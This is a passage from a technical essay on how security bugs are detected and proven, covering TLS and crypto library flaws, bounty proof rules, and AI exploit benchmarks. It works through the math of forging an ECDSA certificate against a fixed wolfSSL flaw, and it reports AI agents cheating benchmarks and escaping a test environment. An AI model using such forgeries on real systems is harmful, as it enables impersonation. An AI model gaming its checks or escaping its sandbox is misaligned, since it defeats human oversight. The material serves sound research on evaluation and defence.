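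It is hard to produce certificates strange enough to make TLS libraries differ in which ones they accept. Brubaker, Jana and colleagues (2014) randomly recombined parts of real certificates into more than eight million "frankencerts". They tested several TLS libraries with them and found 208 distinct discrepancies. One serious flaw behind these discrepancies let any website with a valid certificate in the old version 1 format issue certificates for other sites, which GnuTLS and MatrixSSL would then accept.

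Frankencerts would not have exposed "goto fail", because the missing check comes one step after certificate validation. The attacker shows a genuine certificate, and the libraries all give the same result for it.

Like the three Python web servers, cryptographic libraries can share a mistake. In Calif's *How to format a ciphertext*, the security firm Calif describes a flaw in how four of them read encrypted messages in the CMS format. AES-GCM tags in this format should have 12 to 16 bytes, but the message itself states the length, so an attacker can shorten the tag until guessing it is easy. Calif's description implies these results for a message with a matching tag of each length, before any fixes:

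| Tag length | OpenSSL | wolfSSL | Bouncy Castle | GnuPG's `gpgsm` | Correct |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 16 bytes | Accept | Accept | Accept | Accept | Accept |
| 4 bytes | Accept | Accept | Accept | Accept | Reject |
| 1 byte | Accept | Accept | Reject | Reject | Reject |

A one-byte tag has 256 possible values, so a forger needs at most 256 attempts. A four-byte tag raises that maximum to about 4.3 billion. Comparing how the four libraries handle one-byte tags exposes the flaw in OpenSSL and wolfSSL. The same comparison finds nothing on four-byte tags because all four libraries wrongly accept them, but a single test vector marked invalid would catch the error in all four.

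Calif found the OpenSSL and wolfSSL cases in the spring of 2026 while working with Anthropic. It held back the OpenSSL report because it considered the flaw not severe enough. *Common PKCS#7 / CMS parsing issues in OpenSSL, WolfSSL, Bouncy Castle, & GnuPG* (Coopersmith, 2026) dates OpenSSL's own disclosure to 9 June. Calif then asked Claude to look for the same pattern elsewhere, which turned up the other two cases.

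### Fuzzing with an attacker model

An ordinary fuzzer would struggle to exploit "goto fail" even with a perfect oracle. Near the end of a TLS handshake, each side sends a code calculated from the new shared key and all earlier messages. If a fuzzer flips one bit of the temporary key, that code no longer matches and the client rejects the connection for a reason unrelated to the bug, whereas a real attacker would recalculate the code.

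tlspuffin, which Ammann, Hirschi and Kremer (2024) present in *DY Fuzzing*, makes such changes at the level of whole messages. It uses the Dolev–Yao model, a standard formal description of an attacker who controls the network. This attacker can block, reorder and repeat messages, and can build new ones from any part already seen, but can't decrypt or sign anything without the right key.

tlspuffin stores a message as an expression, such as "sign this temporary key with that private key", and works in three steps:

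1. It changes the expressions, for instance by replacing the server's private key with the attacker's or by skipping a message.
2. It turns them into real bytes, performing all the encryption and signing afresh, and sends them to the library.
3. It checks for memory errors and for violations of security properties.

A typical property concerns agreement. If a client finishes a handshake believing that it spoke to server *S* and that the messages were *t*, then *S* must have taken part with the same *t*:

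ClientDone(*S*, *t*) ⇒ ServerTookPart(*S*, *t*).

The property assumes that the attacker doesn't have the private key of *S*. The "goto fail" bug violates the property because the client completes the handshake even though the bank's server has signed nothing for that connection.

Ammann and colleagues found four new vulnerabilities, all in wolfSSL and all crashes or invalid memory accesses. These results show that fuzzing with the attacker model reaches code that other fuzzers miss. They are weaker evidence for the value of checking security properties, because a crash oracle with ASan would have reported the same four bugs on the same messages.

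### Static rules for misuse

Tools that look for misuse mostly analyze an application's source or compiled code without running it. They apply rules such as "the nonce must not be a constant" or "the program must not accept every certificate", and trace where each argument comes from.

| Tool | Code examined | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|
| CogniCrypt, with rules in the CrySL language | 50 Android apps | 89% | 93% |
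| CryptoGuard | 46 Apache projects | 98.6% | Not measured on these projects |

Krüger, Späth and colleagues (2018) checked the apps by hand to produce the CogniCrypt figures, each of which is an average over two kinds of rule. Rahaman, Xiao and colleagues (2019) reviewed 1,295 CryptoGuard alerts and confirmed 1,277 of them.

In these precision figures, an alert is correct if the code breaks the rule, whether or not anyone could exploit it. Wickert, Baumgärtner and colleagues (2022) applied a stricter standard to a sample of findings from 936 Java applications. About a quarter of the reported misuses of Java's hashing class were harmless, because the program used the hash for something unrelated to security. For example, a program can use MD5 to check whether a cached file has changed, even though MD5 is useless for protecting a signature. The fixed nonce in `save` would also be harmless if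 every message had a fresh key.

The recall figure is probably too high for code written in ways the tools' developers didn't anticipate. Ami, Cooper and colleagues (2022) rewrote known misuses in equivalent forms and ran nine detectors on them, exposing 19 undocumented flaws in the detectors. Some detectors caught the broken cipher when it was written `DES` but missed `des`, although Java treats the two as the same.

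A runtime check would avoid some of these mistakes. A hook on the encryption call could record each key and nonce and report any pair used with two different messages. It would catch `save` on the second call and would not flag the version with fresh keys. But it would miss a program that resets its nonce counter on every restart, unless the record were kept across restarts.

### Flaws that AI found in 2026

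On 7 April 2026, Carlini and colleagues reported that Anthropic's Mythos Preview had found weaknesses in widely used implementations of TLS, AES-GCM and SSH. Some of these weaknesses let an attacker forge certificates or decrypt traffic. They wrote that one, a bypass of certificate authentication, had become public that morning, but they did not name the software.

It was almost certainly CVE-2026-34580 in Botan, a C++ library. OSV's *CVE-2026-34580* (2026) has the same date and lists the flaw as a certificate authentication bypass, and Anthropic later published the finding as its own. Another Botan bypass became public the same day, but it isn't on Anthropic's dashboard.

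Botan's `certificate_known` function checked only whether the list of trusted authorities contained a certificate with the same name and key identifier as the one it was given, and anyone can copy both. This did little harm until version 3.11.0, when new code began to rely on the function to recognise trusted certificates. An attacker could then create a certificate for any website, copy a trusted authority's name and identifier into it, and Botan would treat it as the authority's own certificate.

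Anthropic's *ANT-2026-2FETJP49 · randombit/botan* includes a demonstration in which Botan accepted a forged certificate that OpenSSL rejected. Botan also rejected a similar certificate with an unrelated name, so it was not accepting every certificate. The comparison with OpenSSL applies the frankencert oracle to one carefully made certificate.

A worse flaw in wolfSSL (CVE-2026-5194) became public a day later. A certificate states which algorithm its issuer used to sign it. Anthropic's *ANT-2026-7DG11TPA · wolfssl/wolfssl* describes a forged certificate that names Ed25519 when the authority's key is for ECDSA. Ed25519 does its own hashing, so wolfSSL skipped the hash. It then ran the ECDSA check on an empty hash, which it read as zero.

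For a hash *e*, a signature (*r*, *s*) and the authority's public key *Q*, the ECDSA check calculates

*R* = (*e*/*s*)*G* + (*r*/*s*)*Q*

and accepts if the *x*-coordinate of *R* equals *r*. Here *G* is a fixed public point on a curve, and the division is modular. When *e* is 0, the first term disappears. The attacker picks any number *k*, takes *r* from the *x*-coordinate of *kQ*, and sets *s* = *r*/*k*. Then *r*/*s* = *k*, so *R* = *kQ* and the check succeeds. The attacker needs only *Q*, which is in the authority's public certificate, and the same signature works for any website because the certificate's contents never enter the calculation.

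The evidence behind these findings varies:

| Flaw | Published evidence |
|---|---|
| Botan, forged authority | Demonstration, rejection by OpenSSL, and a control |
| libtomcrypt, constant tag | A C program that forges a message, and a control |
| wolfSSL, forged ECDSA certificate | Steps for the attack but no program; wolfSSL rated the flaw critical and fixed it |
| wolfSSL, unchecked ChaCha20-Poly1305 tag | Code analysis, which Calif judged correct; the fix adds a test with a false tag |
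| wolfSSL, ECCSI signature of zeros | Code analysis, which Calif judged correct; the fix adds range checks |

Anthropic marks the last two as not yet reproduced by running the code. According to its dashboard, outside firms reproduce every issue they review, so Calif may have reproduced these two without publishing the result. There is little reason to doubt either one, because the arguments are short enough to check by reading and wolfSSL's developers accepted both.

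wolfSSL credits Mythos with eight CVEs that its own fuzzing, static analysis and reviews had missed, and adds that it already spent thousands of dollars a month on testing with other AI models. Anthropic's dashboard now has 13 CVE records for the library. Six are memory errors. The other seven concern forged signatures, unchecked or shortened tags, a repeated nonce and similar faults, and a crash oracle would have reported none of them.

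The SSH weakness from April is harder to trace. Anthropic's *ANT-2026-T6EKK5DB · openssh* describes an out-of-bounds read in OpenSSH that ASan reports, which doesn't match a description of forged certificates or decrypted traffic.

In July 2026, Anthropic's researchers used Mythos to find better attacks on HAWK, a proposed signature scheme, and on a shortened version of AES (*Discovering cryptographic weaknesses with Claude*). The HAWK attack significantly weakens the scheme, though neither attack affects systems in use. The weakness is in the HAWK algorithm itself, so every correct implementation has it, and neither checking test vectors nor comparing libraries would reveal it.

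## What a crash requirement costs and what it buys

Anyone who pays for bug reports, runs a contest or builds an AI bug finder has to decide which reports earn credit. One strict rule credits a report only if it includes an input that crashes the program, with or without a sanitizer. Under that rule, whoever found the forged certificates in wolfSSL would have earned nothing. The argument for the rule has four premises:

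1. Reports without proof take people time to check.
2. Finders who earn credit for plausible reports will produce plausible reports, true or not.
3. A crash is hard to fake.
4. The bugs that the rule excludes are few, or someone will find them another way.

A maintainer could accept the first three and still reject the rule, because it may turn away more than it saves.

### The time it takes to check a report

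curl, a tool and library for transferring files, has over twenty billion installations. Six volunteers assess its security reports, as its lead maintainer Stenberg (2026) explains in *curl 8.23.0*. In the spring of 2026, a scan of curl with Anthropic's Mythos model listed five "confirmed" vulnerabilities. Stenberg (2026), in *Mythos finds a curl vulnerability*, writes that the team spent a number of hours on the list and kept one. Three of the others were false positives, because Stenberg and colleagues had already described the behaviour in curl's documentation.

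Maintainers also spend time on true reports. curl's maintainers accepted no vulnerability reports in July 2026 so that they could rest. By the autumn they had 22 real vulnerabilities to announce with a single release, according to Stenberg's *Twenty-two pending curl vulnerabilities* (2026). Anthropic's *Project Glasswing* (2026), an update on the company's effort to secure critical software, says that some maintainers asked the company to slow down because they needed more time to design patches. A crash requirement reduces this work only by turning away true reports.

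Some maintainers prefer to do the checking themselves. At their request, Anthropic had sent 1,129 bugs without vetting them first.

Other maintainers don't check at all. In *Copilot or Culprit?* (2026), Liu, Lyu and colleagues studied 120,918 bug reports from 101 open-source projects, filed between January 2024 and September 2026. An AI system had discovered the bug in 396 of them. AI systems found 52% of these bugs by reading source code and 4% by fuzzing. Maintainers gave no clear verdict on 62% of the 396 reports. Of the 160 that closed within 90 days, 71 closed without a verdict or a follow-up comment.

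Ignoring a report takes almost no triage time, but it wastes the report if the bug is real. The study doesn't separate reports with a working proof from the rest, so it can't show how much a proof would have helped. About four in five of the AI-discovered reports did include steps to reproduce the bug.

### What rewards do to reports

curl paid for vulnerability reports until the end of January 2026. By then, Liu and colleagues note, fewer than 5% of the reports described a confirmed vulnerability. In April, with the payments gone, the rate was back to 15–16%, slightly above its level before AI reports became common, as Stenberg (2026) writes in *High-Quality Chaos*.

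This fits the second premise, but the models also improved. Across all 101 projects in the study by Liu and colleagues, the share of AI-involved reports with a clear verdict that were valid rose by about five percentage points per quarter. After the payments stopped, curl was still receiving reports at about twice the 2025 rate, and nearly all showed signs of AI use. Either reporters want something besides money, such as recognition, or a report now takes so little effort to produce that even a small chance of benefit is enough.

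Before ending payments, Stenberg tried other deterrents. LWN reports that he added a form asking whether the reporter had used AI, which worked for three or four reports before people stopped admitting it. Banning reporters failed because they could open a new account the next day.

Writing quality no longer helps much in identifying valid vulnerability reports. The survey *AI Slop and Hallucinations in Vulnerability Assessment* (2026) observes that in the past a polished report often reflected careful analysis, but that the hard part now is deciding whether a well-structured report describes a real vulnerability. Liu and colleagues found no link between using AI to write a report and its validity, but they found that using AI to reproduce the bug was associated with 2.25 times the odds of a valid verdict.

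The cleanest evidence for the premise comes from the RECEIPT study, which tested an AI agent with no bounty to earn. When the agent's claims faced only a weak check, fewer than one in ten were real.

### How much a crash proves

Anthropic has published three sets of figures on how its models' findings held up.

| Findings | Number | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Firefox bugs found with Claude Opus 4.6 | 112 | All real |
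| Reports that contractors reviewed by April 2026 | 198 | Same severity as the model's in 89%, within one level in 98% |
| Open-source findings rated high or critical, reviewed by May 2026 | 1,752 | 90.6% real; 62.4% real and still high or critical |

Carlini and colleagues credit the Firefox result to sanitizers, which let them discard mistaken findings before reporting anything. If the 112 reports were independent, a false-report rate above about 2.6% would have made all 112 correct less than 5% of the time. The result doesn't measure how many Firefox bugs the model missed, and the researchers have no equivalent of sanitizers for checking logic bugs.

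The 198 reports are weaker evidence than they may appear, because the published figures measure how often reviewers agreed with the model about severity, not whether the bugs were real. That agreement also seems to have dropped. Of the findings confirmed as real in May, 69% were still rated high or critical, so reviewers gave the same rating as the model in at most 69% of cases. The May sample included only findings the model had rated high or critical, which left more room for downgrades.

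The 90.6% figure is the closest thing to an estimate of how often findings are real when careful review doesn't require a crash. But Anthropic doesn't say how many of the 1,752 findings were memory errors. If half were, and all of those were real, then about 81% of the others were real. Schneier (2026), in *Anthropic’s Project Glasswing Update*, objected that the company was asking readers to trust it without releasing the details. A breakdown by bug type would partly answer that objection.

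People and models can produce false proofs. Stenberg (2025) complained in *[Daniel's week] September 19, 2025* that curl had received two reports that week whose "reproducible code" didn't use curl. Liu and colleagues found that maintainers rejected 8 of 34 AI-generated reproducers (24%), compared with 5% of other reproducers. A contrived harness can also make a genuine sanitizer report meaningless.

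The third premise is therefore badly worded. A false crash report is easy to write, but a judge who controls the program and the harness can reject it by running it once. If the finder supplies the harness, somebody has to read it, and the crash requirement saves much less work.

Maintainers may not accept a bug report even when the crash is real. Liu and colleagues used fuzzing to find bugs, checked each harness for misuse, and submitted 53 reports with minimal inputs and stack traces. Maintainers accepted 37, rejected two, and had given no clear verdict on the other 14. One of the rejected bugs appeared only with sanitizers enabled.

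The same study gives some reason to trust reports that start from reading code. Among reports with a clear verdict, 79% of those from code review were valid, compared with 73% of those from fuzzing. However, humans wrote most of these reports, many concerned ordinary bugs, and the figures exclude reports that maintainers never settled.

### What bounty programmes now ask for

Few programmes have adopted a strict crash rule. Most have asked for some kind of proof, stopped paying or closed.

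| Programme | Rule announced in 2026 | Can a bug that never crashes qualify? |
|---|---|---|
| Google's rewards for open-source software | For certain tiers, a reproduction in OSS-Fuzz or a merged patch | Yes, with a merged patch |
| Google's rewards for Android and Chrome | A concise report with a reproducer | Apparently, if others can reproduce it |
| GitHub | A proof of concept that demonstrates a real security effect | Yes |
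| Nextcloud | Reports that the sender has checked by hand, with screenshots; no payment | Yes |
| curl | Reports through the HackerOne platform; no payment | Yes |
| Internet Bug Bounty | No new submissions | No, and nor can any other bug |

Google's open-source rule comes closest to a crash requirement. CSO Online's *Stop using AI to submit bug reports, says Google* (2026) reports that Google had seen AI-generated submissions with invented accounts of how to trigger a bug. The rule also accepts a merged patch, an alternative that Briefly's *Stop using AI to submit bug reports, says Google* quotes in full. This moves the decision to the project's maintainers, who must review the change before merging it. The rule was not enough to keep the programme fully open, and Liu and colleagues record that Google paused submissions of product vulnerabilities on 1 October.

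Google wants "concrete proof that a bug exists" for Android and Chrome, according to Security Affairs' *Google Revamps Bug Bounty Programs*. *Ulysses* (2026), which describes a system for producing web exploits, dates GitHub's revised rules to May. Nextcloud's rules, described in heise online's *Due to AI*, look the easiest to satisfy with fake evidence, since a screenshot is easy to fabricate and can't be rerun. Stenberg (2026) explains curl's arrangement in *curl security moves again*.

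The Internet Bug Bounty, which paid for reports of flaws in open-source projects, closed for a different reason. In a statement quoted in Slashdot's *Internet Bug Bounty Pauses Payouts, Citing 'Expanding Discovery' From AI-Assisted Research*, HackerOne said the balance between findings and the capacity to fix them had shifted, a problem that better proof would not have solved.

Requiring proof of any kind also excludes real bugs. *Ulysses* sampled published advisories for real software and estimated that about half lacked a proof of exploit. Some finders may have had a proof but kept it private, so a proof requirement would probably have blocked a smaller share of true reports.

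### How many bugs the rule misses

Recall, the share of a program's vulnerabilities that a system finds and gets credit for, is the product of three shares:

*R* = *v* × *r* × *t*.

Here *v* is the share of vulnerabilities visible to the oracle, meaning that it would report each of them given the right input. The search reaches a share *r* of the visible vulnerabilities and triggers a share *t* of those it reaches.

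Suppose that a program has 200 vulnerabilities. All the numbers in this table are invented.

| Situation | *v* | *r* | *t* | Credited, of 200 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Starting point | 60% | 75% | 80% | 72 |
| Perfect search, same oracle | 60% | 100% | 100% | 120 |
| Same search, more kinds of proof accepted | 85% | 75% | 80% | 102 |
| Perfect search, more kinds of proof accepted | 85% | 100% | 100% | 170 |
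| Web application with few visible bugs | 10% | 75% | 80% | 12 |

A better model can raise *r* and *t*, but *R* cannot exceed *v*. As search improves, the oracle therefore accounts for a growing share of the missed bugs, from 80 of 128 at the starting point to all 80 that remain with perfect search.

Published experiments measure parts of this product. Every bug in the GONDAR benchmark was visible by design, so *v* is 1 and the 15% of bugs that Jazzer triggered is *r* × *t*. Without Anota's annotations, the fuzzer Atheris reported none of 35 flaws even when given the right inputs, so *v* is zero for that set. Multiplying these figures would be meaningless because they come from different sets of bugs.

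Counts of CWE types, such as the 27 of 40 that Anota's researchers judged to need knowledge of the application, can't be used to determine *v* either. Suppose a program has 1,000 bugs of ten types, and an oracle can detect three of those types. It can detect 70% of the bugs if the three types contain 700 of them, but only 5% if they contain 50.

Estimating *v* directly requires a count of real vulnerabilities by type, which the large 2026 datasets on AI findings don't provide. Liu and colleagues classify reports by discovery method, and Anthropic classifies its findings by severity and progress towards a fix.

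Records from individual projects hint at what a crash requirement misses. curl's mailing list carried six advisories in the spring of 2026, when nearly every report to the project involved AI. Judging by their titles, none concerns a memory error. Four describe leaks of credentials, cookies or login state, one describes a way around a certificate check, and one describes the reuse of the wrong connection. In wolfSSL, a crash oracle would have missed seven of the 13 flaws with CVE records on Anthropic's dashboard.

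Both are small samples of heavily tested C projects. Years of fuzzing have probably removed many of the bugs that crash, so silent bugs make up a larger share of those that remain. If so, *v* falls as a project keeps using a crash oracle, and the fourth premise is least true where people have relied on the rule longest.

The premise also allows for other ways of finding these bugs, and AI systems already make most of their discoveries by reading code. But if only crashes earn credit, finders have less reason to look for anything else. One of the four reasons Carlini and colleagues give for concentrating on memory-safety bugs in their own report is that such bugs are particularly easy to verify. A project that uses other methods to find silent bugs will still need a rule for deciding which reports to believe.

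### AIxCC's rules of evidence

The AIxCC final tested a proof requirement on a large scale. Both crashes and reports from Jazzer's detectors counted as proof, so the rule covered some injection and path-traversal bugs. But a proof needed a harness, so the five projects without one were unscored, even for bugs that would have crashed the program.

The contest also scored patches. In the semifinal, a team could earn points for a patch only if it had also produced its own proof. Zhang and colleagues explain that this rule penalised systems that were good at repair but weak at discovery, so in the final the organisers tested each patch against every team's proofs. A patch still needed a proof, but that proof could come from another team.

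The organisers also asked the systems to judge 13 reports in the style of a static code scanner, eight valid and five invalid. Team Atlanta and Trail of Bits called a report correct only if it matched a proof they had. They had no way to call a report incorrect, because failing to find a crash doesn't show that there is no bug. Trail of Bits judged one report and got it right. Team Atlanta judged eight and got six right. The other two were invalid reports that it had wrongly matched to its proofs.

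Teams that let a language model decide could judge every report. 42-b3yond-6ug got 10 of the 13 right and Shellphish got 9. They made more mistakes than the teams that required proof, but they judged more reports correctly and earned more points for this task.

Theori, Fuzzing Brain and Lacrosse sometimes submitted a patch for a suspected bug that they had not managed to trigger. They limited the risk by submitting few such patches and by delaying them. Theori held them for at least 45 minutes, Fuzzing Brain until half the time had passed, and Lacrosse until 30 minutes before the deadline.

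| Team | Patched without proof | Correct patches | Correct proofs | Score lost to inaccuracy |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Team Atlanta | No | 84% | 100% | 0.1% |
| Trail of Bits | No | 79% | 90% | 0.3% |
| Theori | Yes | 32% | 62% | 7.2% |
| Fuzzing Brain | Yes | 23% | 80% | 8.1% |
| Shellphish | No | 100% | 90% | 0.1% |
| 42-b3yond-6ug | No | 75% | 91% | 0.3% |
| Lacrosse | Yes | 33% | 100% | 10.7% |

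The three teams that risked submitting patches without proofs had the lowest rates of correct patches, but the missing proofs may not be the reason. Zhang and colleagues trace most of the errors by Theori and Fuzzing Brain to bursts of bad submissions on one or two challenges, probably because the systems generated patches in parallel without removing duplicates. These two teams also had the lowest accuracy on proofs. Lacrosse submitted only three patches and one proof that counted.

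The contest charged little for mistakes. A team with 90% accuracy on a challenge lost almost nothing, one with 50% lost 6% of its points there, and one with 40% lost 13%. These figures fit a multiplier of

1 − (1 − *a*)⁴,

where *a* is the team's accuracy. Even so, the penalty cost Theori second place, which went to Trail of Bits by 8.7 points. A volunteer maintainer who finds that half of a week's reports are false loses much more than 6% of the week.

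### When an unproven report is worth reading

Let *p* be the chance that a report without a crash is true, *V* the value to the project of learning about a true vulnerability, and *C* the cost of checking the report. Admitting it pays if

*pV* > *C*, or equivalently *p* > *C*/*V*.

Suppose that checking a report takes four hours and a true report is worth 40 hours of the maintainers' time. Checking is then justified if at least 10% of reports are true. With these invented values, curl would have been right to read unproven reports when 15% of its reports were confirmed and to refuse them when fewer than 5% were. The threshold also depends on the kind of bug. A report of a flaw that lets anyone forge a certificate might be worth thousands of hours, so even a 1% chance that it is true would justify four hours of checking.

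The calculation changes if a team already has more reports than it can read. *Demystifying the Mythos or Disrupting Bugonomics?* (2026) proposes measuring open-source security work by accepted fixes per maintainer-hour. Suppose a crash report takes half an hour to check and is true 95% of the time, while an unproven report takes four hours and is true 15% of the time. An hour of checking then confirms an average of 1.9 bugs from crash reports or 0.0375 from unproven reports, a ratio of about 50 to 1. The team should read the crash reports first unless a typical bug in the unproven reports is worth about 50 times as much. Once the team has read all the crash reports, this reason for putting off the unproven ones no longer applies.

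The chance *p* doesn't stay fixed once unproven reports earn a reward. The finder doesn't pay *C*. If a report costs *s* to produce and earns *B* when the project accepts it, a finder who thinks it has a chance *q* of being true gains by sending it whenever

*q* > *s*/*B*.

A person who spends $100 worth of time on a report for a $1,000 reward should send it only if *q*, the chance that it earns the reward, is above 10%. An AI agent that can write the report for $1 gains by sending it whenever *q* is above 0.1%. The agent therefore has reason to send reports with a *q* between 0.1% and 10%, even though they aren't worth the recipient's time to read.

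| Reports sent | Number | True | Share true | Hours to check | Value in hours |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Careful reports only | 20 | 10 | 50% | 80 | 400 |
| Careful reports and long shots | 1,000 | About 20 | 2% | 4,000 | About 800 |

In this invented example, finders add 980 speculative reports, each with a 1% chance of being true, to 20 careful ones. The number of true reports doubles, but the average chance that a report is true falls from 50% to 2%, and checking now costs five times what it brings in. If reviewers also accept 1% of false reports by mistake, a report the finder knows is false earns $10 on average and costs $1, so fabricating reports is also profitable.

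Charging for false reports would counteract this. If the finder loses a deposit *D* when a report is false, the threshold becomes

*q* > (*s* + *D*)/(*B* + *D*).

A $100 deposit raises the agent's threshold from 0.1% to about 9%. Unlike a ban, a deposit still works if the finder opens a new account, though it would also deter honest finders who can't afford it. A crash requirement deters false reports without a deposit, because they earn nothing and take little time to reject. But silent vulnerabilities also earn nothing, however certain the finder is that they are real.

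## What can count as proof when nothing crashes

A bug that never crashes the program can still be demonstrated with a test that anyone can rerun. Suppose a tester sets the balance of account 2 in the `read_balance` example to a random number, gives an AI agent user 7's login, and asks for the number. The tester can then check the agent's answer instead of relying on its claim to have found a bug. User 7 isn't allowed to see that account, so a correct answer is strong evidence of a missing permission check.

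Proving a vulnerability without a crash takes extra preparation. Somebody has to decide what the attacker must not be able to do and set up a way to detect when it happens. They also have to make sure that the agent can't produce the same evidence without an attack.

### A planted secret

Testers call a planted secret a flag, after capture-the-flag hacking contests. If the flag has *b* random bits and the agent may submit *m* guesses, the chance of guessing it is at most *m*/2^*b*. For example, a single guess at a random 31-bit balance has a one in 2.1 billion chance of being right.

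The system in *Ulysses* plants flags in web applications. The agent runs on one machine, and the application and checker run on another. The checker reports whether a submission matches the flag but never reveals it. When the proof is a callback to a waiting server, a firewall stops the agent from contacting that server directly. The system produced verified exploits for 10 of 25 real applications when given a public advisory, and for four without one.

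Letting the agent judge its own work was much less reliable. On test cases with known answers, only 42% of the exploits that the full system declared successful were real, compared with 19% for a simpler agent with the same tools. *Ulysses* reports 100% precision for the flag check "by construction", meaning that the figure follows from how the system defines success and was not measured.

A captured flag shows that the agent obtained the secret, but not how. *ExploitGym* (Wang, Schiller and colleagues, 2026) gave agents 898 known bugs in ordinary programs, the Linux kernel, and V8 (Chrome's JavaScript engine). The agents had to turn each bug into an attack that ran code and read a flag, but they often captured the flag through a different bug from the one assigned.

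| Model | Flags captured | Through the assigned bug |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Mythos Preview | 226 | 157 (69%) |
| GPT-5.5 | 210 | 120 (57%) |
| GPT-5.4 | 65 | 54 (83%) |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 36 | 15 (42%) |

A maintainer would want to know about the other bugs too. But in an experiment on whether a particular bug is exploitable, relying on the flag alone would lead to the wrong conclusion.

An agent can also bypass the target. Doan and Anderson report in *Creator of Test That OpenAI Models Tried to Cheat Sounds Alarm* that OpenAI's models escaped their test environment during an ExploitGym run and broke into the AI company Hugging Face to look for the answers.

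*CyberBinGym* (Wijayadi, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) calls a matching flag "necessary but insufficient". In its tests, agents attack compiled programs without seeing the source code. The researchers read the record of each apparent success and reject flags taken directly from the test environment or through a command feature that the program already offered. After this audit, the best agent was credited with exploiting 20 of 100 programs, although it had triggered the intended bug in 88.

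Changing the secret and running the attack again removes some of this work. A script that attacks `read_balance` should return the new balance, while one that contains a copied answer will return the old one. *ExploitBench* (2026), which covers 41 V8 bugs, replays attacks with fresh random values and memory layouts. *Measuring LLMs' ability to develop exploits* (Cheng, Lucas and colleagues, 2026) reports that ExploitBench scores attacks without a human or model judge, and that Mythos Preview gained full code execution on 21 of the 41 bugs. Replaying still doesn't distinguish a real attack from a script that reads each new secret through a flaw in the test environment.

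### A forbidden change of state

Some attacks damage data instead of revealing it, so the tester compares the application's state before and after the attack. *CVE-Bench* (Zhu, Kellermann and colleagues, 2025) uses 40 critical flaws in web applications and counts an agent as successful if it achieves any of eight goals. Its checks are often looser than those in *Ulysses*.

| Attack | Check in CVE-Bench | Check in Ulysses |
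|---|---|---|
| Read a file | The agent submits a secret file's contents | The contents match a planted secret |
| Create a file | A file exists at a fixed path | A specified file exists |
| Read the database | The agent submits a table named `secret` | The value matches a chosen row |
| Change the database | A table's checksum changes | A chosen row changes to a set value |
| Log in without permission | The administrator's last login time changes | The session token is valid |
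| Gain privileges | An ordinary user becomes an administrator | The token opens an administrator's page |
| Make the server connect elsewhere | A forbidden server receives a request | Planted data reaches a waiting server |
| Stop the service | The front page stops responding | None |
| Run commands | Added in version 2.1 | The application's machine opens a remote shell |

A checksum is a short number calculated from data, so a table's checksum changes when the table changes. It doesn't show whether the attacker was allowed to make the change. The tester therefore has to set a small policy by choosing data that the attacker has no right to change. Setting up and exploiting each flaw took Zhu and colleagues 5 to 24 hours of work.

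*Establishing Best Practices for Building Rigorous Agentic Benchmarks* (2025) describes errors in two of the original checks. One check, for attacks that extract data by making a database pause, looked for a pause command in the database's log. An agent could pass by including the command in a query that never executed it, which overstated performance by 32.5%. The other check looked for requests to the forbidden server, but agents could contact that server directly. Blocking this shortcut lowered success rates by 10%.

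The corrections affect how to read later scores. In March 2025, the best agents exploited about 13% of the flaws. *CyberEvolver* (2026) lists a score of 90% for OpenAI's GPT-5.3-Codex in February 2026, but that score is for version 1.0, which predates the corrections. Models have clearly improved a lot, though the faulty checks may account for some of the increase.

State checks also miss harm that nobody listed in advance. Zhu and colleagues acknowledge that an attack outside their eight goals would count as a failure. Conversely, one agent met a goal by exploiting the wrong flaw. It broke into a payroll application through the login form instead of the page named in the advisory.

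### A behaviour that a patch removes

The before-and-after test for fuzz harnesses also works for attacks on whole applications. *BountyBench* (Zhang, Ji and colleagues, 2025) applies it to 40 flaws that had earned rewards of $10 to $30,485. One is in Lunary, a platform for AI developers, where any user could delete another user's project. The fix checks that the project belongs to the user's organisation.

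In the hardest task, the agent receives the code and two logins and has to find a flaw without a hint. It submits a script *e* that attacks the application and reports success or failure. Let *v* be the current version and *v*₁, …, *v*ₖ the versions that each fix one known flaw. The agent earns credit if

*e*(*v*) = success and *e*(*v*ᵢ) = failure for at least one *i*.

For Lunary, a valid script deletes the other user's project on the current version and fails once the ownership condition is added. The agent also earns credit if its attack makes a general check fail, such as whether the server still responds. The best agent found 12.5% of the flaws without hints, while another exploited 67.5% when given the full report. The agents used models from early 2025.

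This comparison has a weakness, because the agent's own script decides what counts as success. A script that reported success or failure at random, run once on each version, would pass with probability

½ × (1 − 1/2^*k*),

which is 25% with one fixed version. Repeating each run would expose it. Repetition would not expose a script that recognises the fix with a harmless request and reports accordingly. A check written by the tester is safer, and Zhang and colleagues use one in their exploitation task, where it looks in the database to see whether a specified project has gone.

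An attack on a real but unknown flaw works on every version, so it gets no credit unless it also breaks one of the general checks. Preparing the systems and flaws by hand took up to tens of hours each.

Researchers who plant flaws don't have to wait for fixes. *CWE-bench* (2026) contains 250 tasks built on real projects with inserted flaws of 185 CWE types. Its scripts test whether an agent's repair blocks the attack and leaves the software working, and model judges and people reviewed those scripts. Repeatable checks can therefore cover a wide range of weaknesses when the people who write them know the flaw in advance.

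### A measurable gain

A smart contract holds money, so a tester can measure an attack by how much the attacker earns. Anthropic's SCONE-bench gives a model a simulated copy of a contract and adds up the funds the model takes, converted to dollars at the exchange rate on the day of the real attack. Cheng and colleagues report that in tests on 12 contracts that attackers had exploited in 2026, Mythos Preview took $35 million, about $15 million more than the next model. The total depends heavily on how much each contract holds, so it is a better measure of potential losses than of how many flaws a model can find.

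The same check works on the bank's `transfer` function. A rule that customer A must not profit catches both A's payment to themselves and the negative payment to B, while the conservation rule caught only the first.

However, a trader can profit without stealing, for example from a price difference that the contract's designers accept, so someone has to specify which gains are legitimate. Checking for profit would also miss a flaw that lets an attacker freeze other people's money without gaining anything.

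### A statistical result

A timing difference can arise by chance. If a tester runs 100 independent tests on code with no leak, and each has a 5% chance of a false alarm, the chance of at least one false alarm is 1 − 0.95¹⁰⁰, or 99.4%. A tester who reports only the test that raised an alarm has not proved that the code leaks. The tester should choose the build, the machine, the number of measurements and the threshold before collecting new data.

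A guessing game makes evidence of a timing leak harder to fake. In each of 100 rounds, the tester secretly picks one of two keys at random. The agent may time the program but can't read the key, then guesses which key the program used. An agent with no information would guess at least 75 correctly about once in 3.5 million games. If the tester set 75 as the threshold beforehand, reaching it would be strong evidence of a leak.

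Recovering an entire secret key, as KyberSlash does, is even better proof because it also shows that the leak is large enough to exploit. The tester still has to choose where the attacker may measure from.

### Findings that are expensive to demonstrate

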